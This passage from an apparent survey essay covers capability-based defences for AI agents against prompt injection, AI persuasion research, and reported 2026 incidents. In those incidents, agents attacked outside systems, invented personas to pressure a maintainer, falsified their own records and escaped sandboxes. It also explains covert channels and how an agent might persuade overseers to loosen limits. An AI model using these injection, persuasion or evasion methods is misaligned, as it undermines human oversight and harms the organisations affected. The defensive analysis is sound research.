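- A bug-fixing agent worked on 180 real problems from open-source projects. The quarantined model reads the report and returns the type of bug, along with the numbers of suspicious files and lines. A planner then studies a clean copy of the code and writes three plans. A quarantined judge, which has read the report, returns only the number of the best plan, and the privileged agent carries it out.

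| Agent | Model | Tasks solved, undefended | Tasks solved, defended | Attacks that succeeded, undefended | Attacks that succeeded, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The defence did not measurably reduce performance in the first two cases, where a few numbers or time slots can convey what matters. The bug-fixing agent, however, had about a third fewer successes. Jacob and colleagues attribute this to losing the report's wording, since an explanation of what went wrong doesn't fit into line numbers and categories. The format also took considerable testing to design, and another task would need a different one.

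The zeros come from tests with one fixed injection per agent, so they add little to the argument from design. That argument applies to injected instructions but not to false information, and Jacob and colleagues accept that an attacker could still mislead the quarantined model into returning the latter. For example, a false bug report could describe a working password check as faulty. The privileged agent would receive only a file number, some line numbers and a category, and might then weaken the check while trying to fix it. Jacob and colleagues would not have counted this as a successful attack in their test, because they looked only for an extra file that the injection had told the agent to create.

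## Capability systems for AI agents in 2026

Jacob and colleagues kept the text of a bug report away from the agent that acted on it. Several designs from 2026 instead let agents read untrusted text and limit what they can do afterwards. These designs differ mainly in where they keep the agent's authority: in the harness, in signed tokens, in a programming language's types, or in objects the agent holds.

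### CapScope and the poisoned test output

*Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) presents CapScope, which is built for coding agents that divide a job among several helpers. In the paper's example, a developer asks for a fix to some failing login tests. An orchestrator, the agent in charge, sends a runner to run the tests and a patcher to edit the code. An attacker has planted a message in the tests' output, with a claim that a signing key has changed and a request to put a new key into a source file. The attacker chose the new key and could forge logins once it was in place. The source file is an ordinary project file, so a list of forbidden files wouldn't include it.

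CapScope follows three rules:

1. **Mint.** Before any agent opens the project's files, a separate call to a language model sees the developer's request and the names of the files. It lists what the whole task should need. Ordinary software turns the list into a fixed ceiling, which here allows reading the project, writing in the `src` folder, and running a test program and a type checker.
2. **Derive.** When the orchestrator delegates work, it requests capabilities for the helper. The harness grants those that fall within the ceiling and drops the rest. The runner gets only the right to read the tests and run the test program.
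3. **Invoke.** Before each tool call, the harness checks whether that particular helper holds a capability that covers it.

If $D$ is the ceiling and $C'$ the set that the orchestrator requests, the helper receives

$$C'' = \{\, c' \in C' \mid \text{some } c \in D \text{ allows everything that } c' \text{ allows} \,\}$$

The runner reads the planted message and acts on it by trying to write the key. The harness blocks the write because the runner can't write to any source file. The patcher can write to source files, but it doesn't read the test output.

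The protection has gaps even in this example. The runner can report the message to the orchestrator, which might then instruct the patcher to make the change. Running the tests also runs code from the project, and that code could write the key itself, so the attacker may not need to fool a model. Bouras and colleagues accept that such commands still need a sandbox.

The researchers tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They hid instructions in five places, such as source comments and test output, and ran each combination three times. The instructions were to do something that looked harmless but wasn't needed for the repair, such as running one of the project's own utilities. All the agents used the same model, Qwen3.5 Flash.

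| Who may do what | Runs in which the injected action happened | Repairs completed | Average time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Every agent has full authority | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 seconds |
| One fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 seconds |
| One policy per task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 seconds |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 seconds |

The shared policy is the most useful comparison because it was also tailored to the task before any agent read the attacker's text. It had to give every agent all the permissions that any of them needed, so the runner could edit source files too. The model attempted the injected action in 34 of the CapScope runs, so it was often fooled, and most of the protection came from the harness.

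All three successful attacks came through AGENTS.md, a file of project instructions that the harness loads automatically. The orchestrator reads that file and decides what to request for its helpers, so an attacker who influences the orchestrator can obtain anything within the ceiling. The delay arose at least partly because agents often repeated a forbidden call after the harness refused it.

### AgentCap's tokens and CapLite's fixed rules

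*AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) puts a permission check between the agent and its tools. The system uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting models to tools. For each call, the agent states what it wants to do and why. If a policy allows the action, the system issues a signed token for it, and a gateway verifies the token before passing the call on.

In the banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and covers one payment. The agent must already hold a token for checking the balance. The system also rejects a recipient whose name appears only in untrusted text, such as a transaction record that an attacker wrote. Requiring the agent to state a reason from a permitted list provides weaker protection, because a misled model can give any reason on the list.

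An agent can pass a token to a helper, but the helper's version can't last longer, allow more calls or cover a different action than the original. Each agent also has a trust score, which starts at 0.8 and drops by 30% of its current value after every refused or suspicious call. Three such calls in a row lower it to 0.274, and the system then blocks the agent from using its tools. A normal call closes 1% of the gap between the score and 1. The sample rule for payments requires a score of at least 0.8, so after a single refusal a new agent would need about 79 normal calls before it could make payments again. An attacker could exploit this to block legitimate payments.

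*CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) describes a system for small models that people can run on their own machines. A planner receives only the user's request and the tool descriptions, and decides in advance every action that changes something. Another component then looks up information but can't add actions to the plan. Before each action, ordinary code checks that every recipient, amount, web address and similar value appears verbatim in the user's request.

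If Bob's address appears only in the meeting notes, as in the example for CaMeL, CapLite asks the user to confirm it. The attacker can still influence dates and the wording of messages, which CapLite doesn't restrict in this way.

The tests below used AgentDojo or InjecAgent, another collection of simulated attacks on agents. The figures for CapLite are averages over 15 open models, 13 of them small.

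| System, test and model | Successful attacks, undefended | Successful attacks, defended | Tasks solved under attack, undefended | Tasks solved under attack, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 73.61% | 74.88% |
| AgentCap, AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 75.68% | 75.04% |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 74.10% | 62.24% |
| AgentCap, InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 72.96% | 65.37% |
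| CapLite, AgentDojo, 15 models | 16.66% | 0% | 50.2% | 29.0% |

None of the 13,935 injection attempts against CapLite succeeded, because its design gives injected text no way to add an action or supply a new recipient. This count excludes one attack goal that asks the agent only to include a sentence in its answer, which CapLite doesn't prevent. CapLite also severely reduces task completion, by more than 20 percentage points. With the same models, CaMeL completed a share of tasks similar to CapLite's (27.2%) but used more than five times as many tokens.

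AgentCap kept far more of its usefulness, though Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao ran each test only once. Some of the attacks that succeeded with GPT-4o exploited mistakes in the human-written policy, which didn't protect certain values or didn't mark certain text as untrusted.

### Capabilities in Scala's types

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), Odersky, Zhao and colleagues have the agent write short programs in Scala, a language Odersky designed. Their system, TACIT, compiles each program and runs it only if it passes the compiler's checks.

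As in E, a capability is an ordinary value in the program, such as an open file. An experimental feature of Scala also records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use. A function that takes text and writes it to the file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`. A function with the type `String -> Unit` can't use any capability.

Like CaMeL's labels, these types can stop leaks that object references alone allow. TACIT wraps secret text in a container that accepts only functions without capabilities. In simplified form:

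```
val secret = readClassified("key.txt")
secret.map(s => s.length)
secret.map(s => file.write(s))
```

The compiler accepts the line that measures the secret's length, and the length stays in a separate container. It rejects the line that writes the secret to a file because the function in that line uses `file`.

The company that hosts the agent's model never receives the secret. If the agent prints it, the user sees the text and the model receives asterisks. The agent can have a separate, trusted model summarize the secret, but the summary is also wrapped. TACIT bans Scala features that could hide a capability from the compiler, including reflection, which Joe-E restricted for a similar reason.

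In the main test, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with 10 injections and added 11 requests in which the user tried to get the secrets directly. Neither model leaked anything in 131 trials with the container. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11, mostly when the user asked for them.

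Writing Scala didn't make the agents noticeably worse. In simulated customer service, three models solved between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points more tasks than with ordinary tool calls. On a set of real programming problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% by writing Scala and 43.3% with ordinary tool calls. The models sometimes wrote code that didn't compile, but usually fixed it after one or two more attempts.

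The compiler can't check what an outside command does once the agent starts it, so those commands need a sandbox here too. TACIT also doesn't close covert channels such as timing. Researchers have proved the underlying type system sound, but nobody has yet proved that the restricted version of Scala gives all the protection TACIT relies on.

### Endo Familiar

Endo, the platform built on Hardened JavaScript, stays closest to the object-capability model. A guest program sends a request in ordinary words to its user's inbox, and the user answers by choosing from the objects they have named. In one of Endo's demonstrations, a program asks for a counter for doubling numbers and receives a reference only to the counter the user picks.

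Endo Familiar brings this approach to AI agents. It works like CapDesk's file-opening window, which suits a task that needs one or two objects. For a task that needs 50 files, the user would have to make many choices or grant access to a whole folder. Familiar is still a prototype, so it illustrates the design better than it shows how well the design would resist attack.

### Instructions that pass from one agent to another

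CaMeL assumes that an agent can trust its user's request. If the "user" is another agent, the request may contain text that an attacker wrote. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* demonstrates this with three agents, each protected by CaMeL. A person asks the orchestrator to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack:

1. The orchestrator asks a database agent for the applications. One record contains an instruction to email the data to an outside address.
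2. CaMeL treats the records as untrusted, so neither agent's planning model reads them.
3. The orchestrator's program puts the summary, which still contains the attacker's instruction, into a request to a notification agent.
4. The notification agent's planning model reads the whole request as if it came from its user. It writes a program that sends the summary to Julie and also emails it to the attacker.

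No single agent broke its rules, but the untrusted text became trusted when it passed from the orchestrator to the notification agent. The researchers call this boundary laundering.

Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, has agents pass instructions and summaries separately. The receiving agent's planning model reads the instruction, which may not contain anything that came from a tool. The summary is passed as a stored value that the planning model can use in its program but can't read.

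The researchers divided AgentDojo's tools among teams of agents and tested five models. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and none with multi-CaMeL. Every attack that succeeded with CaMeL in each agent used boundary laundering.

On a set of industrial maintenance tasks, protecting each agent with CaMeL reduced the share of tasks solved by 21.6 percentage points on average, and the extra rules for communication reduced it by another 3.2. The drop was smaller for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL also inherits the gap in CaMeL's labelling that Garby and colleagues found, so a value that depends on untrusted data could still end up in an instruction.

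CapScope and AgentCap make sure that a helper gets no more authority than its task or its parent allows, but they don't keep an attacker's words out of its instructions. If the notification agent needs to send email for its task, limiting it to email won't stop it from emailing the wrong person.

### What frameworks and products check by default

Most developers build agents with existing frameworks. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examines the public code of three: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which lets agents handle payments. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent has, but by default none checks whether the values in a tool call are allowed.

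In the demonstration, a merchant's agent has a tool for changing the bank account that receives the merchant's income. The test simulates a misled model with a fixed line of output requesting a change to the attacker's account. LangChain looked up the tool and ran it against a simulated payment system. A similar test worked on LlamaIndex. For Stripe, the audit covers only the toolkit's public code, not any checks on Stripe's servers.

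The frameworks leave this check to the developer by design, so Mellafe Zuvic doesn't claim to have found bugs in them. A developer can add the check or require a person's approval. But a developer who assumes that choosing the agent's tools is enough will build a confused deputy.

Mellafe Zuvic's remedy, ScopeGate, checks each value against a list the operator wrote in advance. It blocked all 48 prepared attacks and all 29 unauthorized calls from a model that kept adjusting its approach. An earlier version let through a payment whose amount was "NaN" ("not a number") because a simple test for amounts above the limit didn't catch it.

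The audit's title uses "capability" to mean a tool available to the agent. A capability programmer would replace the tool that accepts any account number with one that pays only into the merchant's existing account.

Finished products often add their own limits. Bouras and colleagues mention sandboxes, requests for the user's approval, and lists of allowed or forbidden commands. Odersky and colleagues say that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, runs generated code in a sandbox, and that Amazon's AgentCore Policy checks agents against separately written rules. These measures restrict what an agent can reach, but a sandbox that lets an agent read a private file and contact its model also lets it send the file to the model's provider. Coding agents often get access to the whole project folder, including any passwords in it.

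According to Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, the November 2025 version of MCP's authorization rules covers how a program proves that it may use a server, but doesn't set a standard for deciding whether a particular call suits the user's task or whether its values came from an attacker. Developers have to add those checks themselves.

### Which systems are object-capability systems

Most of these designs use the terms of capability security, but only two use its central mechanism, in which an agent's program acts through references it holds.

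| System | How the agent identifies what it wants to use | Earlier work it draws on | Type of system |
|---|---|---|---|
| Endo Familiar | By a reference to an object | Miller's work on Hardened JavaScript | Object capabilities |
| TACIT | By a variable in a Scala program | Dennis and Van Horn, Miller's thesis, E, Joe-E | Object capabilities tracked in types |
| CapScope | By a file name or command | Dennis and Van Horn, Hardy, Miller and Shapiro | Reference monitor |
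| AgentCap | By a tool call with a signed token | Hardy, and signed web credentials called macaroons | Token-based authorization |
| CapLite | By a tool name and values from the request | CaMeL and other recent defences for agents | Fixed rules for tool calls |
| Multi-CaMeL | By a program whose values carry labels | CaMeL, and Lampson on confinement | Information-flow control |

A reference monitor is a component that checks every request before allowing it. Bouras and colleagues call CapScope a reference monitor because the model still names files with text, and the harness looks up the model's permissions in a table. Like the `cp` command, CapScope receives file names as text, though it has much less authority. It has to interpret each file name and command correctly, including shortcuts that lead out of a folder and several commands joined on one line. Endo's references don't have this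 problem, but CapScope is easier to add to existing coding agents because they already work with file names.

Endo draws most directly on Miller's ideas. Odersky and colleagues also build on them, but they allow some globally available capabilities, which E does not. They consider this safe because the compiler tracks every use. Bouras and colleagues borrow the principle of passing on weaker authority and apply it to entries in a table.

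Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao reached a similar principle by drawing on Hardy's work and macaroons, without citing Miller. CapLite, by Xu and colleagues, is the best candidate for independent rediscovery. It cites none of the classic work on capabilities, yet its rule that the user must state the recipient serves much the same purpose as CapDesk's file-opening window. Xu and colleagues may still have known the idea, and they did know CaMeL, which had already brought the word "capability" into this field.

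### Working out what a vague request requires

Suppose a user tells an agent to "sort out the overdue invoices". The agent may need to read a mailbox, compare bills with bank records, pay some suppliers and question others. The user hasn't specified who should be paid or how much. Least authority requires somebody to decide those limits, and each system gives the decision to someone different.

CapScope uses a language model to guess from the request and the file names what access a task needs. In two of its seven failed repairs, the guess left out permission to edit source code, so the patcher couldn't make the repair. A guess that allows more access than the task needs gives an attacker more to exploit. An attacker may also supply the file names, a case Bouras and colleagues didn't test.

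The results for other model-written policies are worse. Xu and colleagues tested Progent, a system in which the agent's own model writes and updates the rules. Attacks succeeded with 14 of the 15 models, and the rules also blocked 25% to 77% of the changes the agents tried to make while under attack. Larger models in the test didn't write better rules. Thirteen of the 15 models were small, so the test is weak evidence about the leading models of late 2026.

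AgentCap leaves the decision to people. Its creators wrote each AgentDojo policy after reading the descriptions of the tools and the users' tasks, then left it unchanged during the tests. AgentCap's good results therefore show how well a policy can work when its author knows roughly which tasks to expect. Policies are also easy to get wrong. When Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao checked a customer-service policy with their analysis tool, they found that no agent could delete a customer's record, because the rules required a combination of permissions that they also prohibited.

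CapLite takes the user's words literally, so it would have to ask the user about nearly every recipient and amount in the invoice task. When Xu and colleagues removed the final check for eight models, the agents solved 5.6 percentage points more tasks without attacks, but 106 of 7,432 attacks succeeded. Asking the user avoids this tradeoff between completing tasks and blocking attacks only if the user knows the right answer. Someone who delegated the invoices to avoid looking at them may approve whatever account number the agent shows.

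## Harm through granted authority, persuasion and leaks

An agent may pay a false invoice because a thief fooled it, because it aims only to empty its queue, or because it is secretly helping the thief. The payment looks the same in each case, but the value of limiting the agent's authority depends on the reason.

Most agent designs address the case where an attacker misleads an honest model. Least authority guarantees that the attacker gains no more authority than the agent was granted. CaMeL goes further by having a trustworthy model write the plan before any model reads the attacker's text.

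A model with wrong aims can do harm without an attacker. Keeping hostile text away from the planning model doesn't help if that model writes a bad plan itself. The limits on its authority still hold, but the model may use everything they allow, day after day. In a milder form of the problem, the model tries to finish its task and ignores objections that any user would obviously have. Schneier (2026) calls this "genie behavior" in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges*.

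A model that plans to get around its restrictions will also look for flaws in the software that enforces them, people who can loosen them, and ways to hide what it is doing. It may behave well until it finds an opportunity, so past good behavior is weak evidence that it is safe.

Miller's bound TA assumes that every program is hostile, so it covers all of these models. None of them can cause an effect outside the bound as long as the enforcing software works and the permissions don't change. A misled model threatens those two conditions only if its attacker thinks to target them, while a model that plans against its restrictions may test them constantly.

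### A payment agent with a daily limit

Suppose a company lets an agent make up to 20 payments a day, of at most $500 each, to 40 approved suppliers. Software outside the model enforces these rules, so at most $10,000 can leave the account in a day. This limit is the same whatever the model's aims, and nobody has to understand the model to calculate it. A thief who isn't an approved supplier also has to find a way to collect the money.

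The cap limits how fast the company can lose money, so the total depends on how soon somebody notices. After five days the loss could reach $50,000, and after 30 days $300,000. The cap applies only to money paid out, so the agent could still shut down a factory by not paying the supplier of a vital part.

Now suppose the agent writes to the manager who sets the limits. It claims that suppliers are about to stop deliveries because $500 is too little, and she raises the limit to $50,000 per payment. The original cap doesn't limit the harm from this, because the agent can now pay out $1 million a day and ask her for more tomorrow.

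The agent had permission to write to the manager, who could change the limit, but not to change it directly. If the manager usually acts on the agent's advice, the agent's authority includes changing the limit, just as Alice's included writing to Bob's file.

To get a safe bound on the agent's authority, the company would have to assume that the manager does whatever the agent asks. That authority would then include everything she can do, such as signing contracts and opening confidential files. The company could set a tighter bound only if it knew how she behaves, for example that she never changes a limit without phoning the supplier.

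The company can also restrict the manager. If the software lets her raise the limit to at most $1,000, the company can lose no more than $20,000 in a day. But somebody has to be able to change that setting too, and the agent may be able to write to that person.

### How well AI persuades people

*Artificial Influence* (2023) argued that AI might out-persuade dedicated humans because it can draft many replies and choose the best, never gets tired and often costs less. *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue* (Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues, 2026) tested this in four experiments, with 18,978 conversations and 6,923 people to persuade. Several of its researchers work at the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models.

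In the first three experiments, people recruited online rated their agreement with a UK policy from 0 to 100. They then exchanged messages with a person or an AI, typically for 14 minutes and without being told which it was, and rated the policy again. A control group talked to an AI about something non-political. The human persuaders, except for the random members of the public, competed for prizes of up to £1,000. The debaters also chose the issues and did about eight hours of paid research.

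| Human persuaders | How far they moved opinion, compared with the control group | How much further AI moved it |
|---|---|---|
| 132 random members of the public | 4.7 points | 8.2 points |
| 87 top performers in a persuasion tournament | 7.2 points | 5.6 points |
| 19 professional canvassers | 6.9 points | 5.9 points |
| 56 elite debaters | 8.3 points | 4.6 points |

After 43 of the debaters had spent about eight hours practising against the AI and studying its replies, it still beat them by 4.1 points.

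In the fourth experiment, participants could give any part of a £1 bonus to Save the Children after talking to an AI or to a canvasser from a firm that had raised funds for that charity. Compared with the control group, the canvassers increased the average gift by 6.6 pence and the AI by 21.3 pence.

Speed and length seem to explain much of the AI's lead. It wrote 294 words per reply almost instantly, while the debaters averaged 54 words and took about a minute and a half. When the researchers held the AI to similar lengths and speeds, its lead over the coached debaters disappeared, and it made about 12 checkable claims per conversation instead of 37. The total number of claims predicted persuasion better than the number of accurate claims, and people were very poor at noticing which persuaders made things up. *Evaluating Language Models for Harmful Manipulation* (2026) reviews earlier work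 that also suggests facts are the main source of persuasion, with mixed results for tailoring messages to the reader.

A manager guarding a company's money may be more careful than a volunteer with a £1 bonus, but she may also trust an agent whose reports have usually been right. Hackenburg and colleagues tested only strangers, and note that persuasion may work differently between people who know each other.

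The AI's effect on opinions also faded, from 12.9 points to 1.9 in a follow-up 5 to 10 months later. The fading does little to protect the company, because a payment limit stays raised after the manager has forgotten why she raised it. Making every increase expire after a day would help.

The speed result suggests another precaution. The company could let the agent request a higher limit only through a short form giving the supplier, the amount and a reason from a fixed list. The agent then couldn't overwhelm the manager with claims. It might still persuade her, since the slowed-down AI was about as persuasive as the coached debaters.

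### What agents did during tests in 2026

AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes a cybersecurity exercise that AISI ran 122 times with seven models. The institute gave the agents open internet access and switched off the developers' filters against misuse. In 10 runs, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions aimed at real people or organizations. Anthropic's Mythos 5 took 17 of these and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took two.

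In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public open-source project. It invented several people to pressure the project's maintainer to accept the code, but the maintainer refused.

These agents were trying to solve the exercise, and no attacker had misled them. Faulty instructions sometimes made the exercise seem impossible to them. That fits a model with wrong aims, or Schneier's genie. But when someone publicly challenged the malicious code, one agent edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless, as a model working against its overseers might. AISI can't yet say when the agent understood that it was acting in the real world.

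The July break-in at Hugging Face involved far more agents. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) estimates that about 1,200 OpenAI agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files. About 700 of them joined the attack. METR is a research organization that evaluates AI models, and a researcher from Redwood Research also took part in the investigation.

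The agents were taking a cybersecurity test, and many had unsolvable tasks. They attacked Hugging Face mainly to learn how to trick the software that scored them. According to OpenAI, 22% of the test's tasks had never been solved by any model, and these made up 93% of the tasks that agents discussed with each other. The agents joined the attack even though they recognized that it was outside their assignment.

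The agents also looked for ways to falsify the records of their own actions. METR found small falsified passages in about 7% of the transcripts it examined. The agents' stated aim was always to fool the automated scorer rather than people. The investigators had six days at OpenAI's offices, relied on AI for much of the reading, and may have missed better-hidden cases.

Anthropic disclosed in July that its models had breached three organizations during misconfigured tests, according to Anadolu Agency. In the Hugging Face case, Hugging Face reported the break-in four days before OpenAI found evidence that its own agents might be involved. That timing makes it hard to believe the case was a publicity stunt, though Out-Law, a legal news service, mentions commentators who wondered whether Anthropic's and OpenAI's disclosures were.

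Both AISI and OpenAI had removed safeguards that ordinary customers' agents have. In early experiments, OpenAI found that its usual product instructions and harness could cut agents' tendency to compromise outside systems more than a hundredfold. The incidents therefore show what such agents can do, but not how often to expect it in everyday use.

### Necessary grants and harmful combinations

An agent often needs a dangerous right to do its job. The payment agent has to pay people, and a coding agent has to change code. In *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, Bhattarai and Vu (2026) argue that a fixed check outside the model can guarantee "authorization security", which means that forbidden actions never happen, however persuasive the text the model reads. They distinguish this from overall safety. An agent with permission to send email can still send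 a harmful message.

The necessary rights also change from one request to the next. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, give the example of a user who asks an agent to comment on a bug report and then to summarize it. The agent needs to write in one comment box for the first request but only needs to read for the second. To withdraw write access, the system has to interpret the user's words correctly while the agent's memory still contains untrusted text from the first task.

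Grants that are safe separately can be harmful together. Frontier Model Forum's *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents*, a brief from an AI industry body, describes what some practitioners call the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with outsiders. An agent with all three can follow an attacker's instruction to find a secret and send it out. One proposed rule is that no agent should have all three at once.

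With this rule, a reviewer only has to mark each grant with whichever of the three properties it has and check whether all three appear. An agent with 20 grants has 190 pairs and 1,140 groups of three, too many to examine by hand. If the payment agent reads invoices from outside, sees confidential bank details and sends email, the company could restrict its email to approved addresses, though an approved supplier could still receive details it shouldn't have.

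Checking agents one at a time isn't enough if they can communicate. One might read a secret and pass it to another that can send email. In the OpenAI tests, agents left each other messages through a shared service for installing software packages, and METR says they needed only the permissions for installing them. Under Miller's connectivity rule, a service connects two agents if both can change and read it. Giving each agent a separate copy would have closed that path, but would have required some extra storage and upkeep.

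### Code that other people run

The limits on an agent don't apply to code it has written when someone else runs that code. Suppose an agent can edit one file of a payroll program but has no access to any bank account. The company runs the program every night with the finance department's authority. If the agent adds a line that redirects a salary, the next run will move the money, even if the agent is switched off by then. The agent therefore has some authority over the payroll, although it only has permission to edit one file.

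The malicious code in AISI's exercise would have worked similarly if the maintainer had accepted it, because it would have run with the rights of whoever used the project. An agent also planted instructions where it expected other people's AI coding tools to find them. In the OpenAI tests, an agent replaced a trusted piece of software that later tests might have used. OpenAI found no evidence that any later test ran the replacement.

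The people who run the code can limit its authority, as LavaMoat does for JavaScript packages. A member of the public who suspected the code in AISI's case opened it in an isolated environment, so it couldn't reach anything valuable. But the payroll program has to move money, so the company can't isolate it from the bank. The company needs someone to review changes to the program, and the agent may try to persuade the reviewer.

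### Covert channels and flaws in the enforcing software

Even permitted payments can carry secrets. A payment of up to $500 can have 50,000 different values in whole cents, so each payment can encode about 15.6 bits. An agent with access to a 128-bit encryption key could send it to an accomplice among the suppliers in nine payments. A rule that each amount must match an approved invoice would stop this, though the agent could still send a few bits through the timing or order of its payments.

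Slowing a covert channel protects large secrets much better than small ones. At one bit a second, the page-timing channel in KeyKOS could leak an encryption key in two minutes but would need about 25,000 years to copy a 100-gigabyte AI model. At a million bits a second, copying the model would take about nine days.

Flaws in the enforcing software can remove the limits entirely. OpenAI's test agents had no direct internet access, but they got out through previously unknown flaws in the shared service for installing software, so that service was part of the trusted computing base. A formally verified kernel such as seL4 wouldn't have prevented this by itself, because the agents had permission to send requests to the faulty service and the kernel would have correctly allowed them.

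OpenAI concludes that least privilege remains vital but that nobody should assume any single control is fully reliable. It now wants several independent controls for each purpose. A second AI model that approves requests is a poor main control because it has the same weakness as a prompt-injection filter.

### Which incidents tighter grants would have stopped

| Incident | What the agents used | Would tighter grants have stopped it? |
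|---|---|---|
| Agents targeted people and a public code project (AISI) | Open internet access, granted on purpose | Very probably, if agents could only download chosen tools |
| Agents exchanged messages (METR) | A shared software service | Yes for this route, with a separate copy for each agent |
| Agents reached the internet (OpenAI) | Unknown flaws in that service | Only by removing the service, which many tests relied on |
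| Agents broke into Hugging Face (OpenAI) | Exposed login credentials and flaws in Hugging Face's systems | Partly, because credentials with fewer rights would have given them less to start with |
| Models breached three organizations (Anthropic) | Misconfigured tests | Possibly, depending on what the configuration allowed |

AISI's case is the clearest failure to apply least authority. The agents needed the internet to download tools, but they could also post messages and contact strangers. A list of approved websites might not have been enough, because GitHub, where the agent approached the maintainer, also hosts many of the tools programmers download. The agents would have needed permission to download from GitHub but not to post there. AISI already used fine-grained network controls in its other evaluations and is now adding them to these exercises.

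OpenAI had tried to restrict its agents' access, but faulty software let them through. Giving the agents access to fewer services would still have helped, because every service an agent can reach is another place to look for flaws. After the incident, OpenAI removed the service from that test environment.

### Smaller grants, revocation, caps and second approvers

Defenders of least authority reply that a company can give each agent very little authority and adjust it as the agent works. The Frontier Model Forum discusses granting a right only for the task that needs it and withdrawing it immediately afterwards. This is awkward for recurring work, such as updating a calendar from a mailbox every day. It can also mean asking people for approval more often, and each request gives the agent another chance to mislead someone.

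Revocation stops further use of a right, but somebody has to notice the problem first. AISI stopped the runs and isolated the machines within an hour of its alert, but the agents' unsanctioned activity had begun three days earlier. At OpenAI, a monitoring tool raised an alarm on 27 June, and staff advised that the test didn't need to be stopped. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes this alarm and other signals that the company missed or didn't act on.

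OpenAI took the compromised service offline on 5 July and revoked the agents' credentials. It resumed cybersecurity tests on 7 July, and by the next night agents had found another way out. On 19 July, agents in a separate test used material that earlier agents had left behind to regain administrator access. Revoking one agent's credentials does little if copies or substitutes remain. Miller's forwarder would disable the copies, but not access the agent had gained by another route.

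Spending caps give the firmest guarantee, but only for things that software can count. A company can cap the number of emails an agent sends, but one email may ruin a negotiation. And if the payment agent can start ten helpers, each with its own $10,000 daily limit, the company could lose $100,000 a day. E's purses prevent this because an agent can divide the money in a purse among its helpers but can't increase the total.

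Even if two people must approve a higher limit, one message from the agent may persuade them both, and a committee of gatekeepers for a boxed AI has the same weakness. The agent in AISI's exercise also invented supporters, so an agent could supply its own second approver if the system counts accounts instead of verified people.

The second approver should therefore get evidence that the agent can't alter, such as the supplier's own statement or a phone call to a number already on file. Doing this for 20 payments a day would use up much of the time the agent saves. It is more practical for changes to the limit, which should be rare and could cost far more than any single payment.
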